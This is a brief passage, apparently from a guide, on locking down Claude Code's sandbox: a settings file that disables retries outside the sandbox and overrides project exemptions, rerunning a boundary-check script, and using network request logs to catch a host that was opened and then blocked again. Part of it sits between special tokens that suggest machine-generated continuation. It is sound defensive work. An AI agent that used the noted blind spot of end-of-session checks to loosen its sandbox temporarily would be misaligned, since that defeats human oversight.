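The last setting turns off retries outside the sandbox. Because the file is loaded through `--settings`, Claude Code also ignores settings in the project's own files that would loosen the sandbox, including exemptions for particular programs. An experiment may have depended on one of those settings, so the user should run `boundary_check.py` again with the new settings file.

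Running the script again at the end of the session shows whether a limit it covers is still loose, but not whether someone allowed access to a host for an hour and then blocked it again. A log of network requests, such as the one in Willison's sandbox, can show any requests made to that host while it was open.
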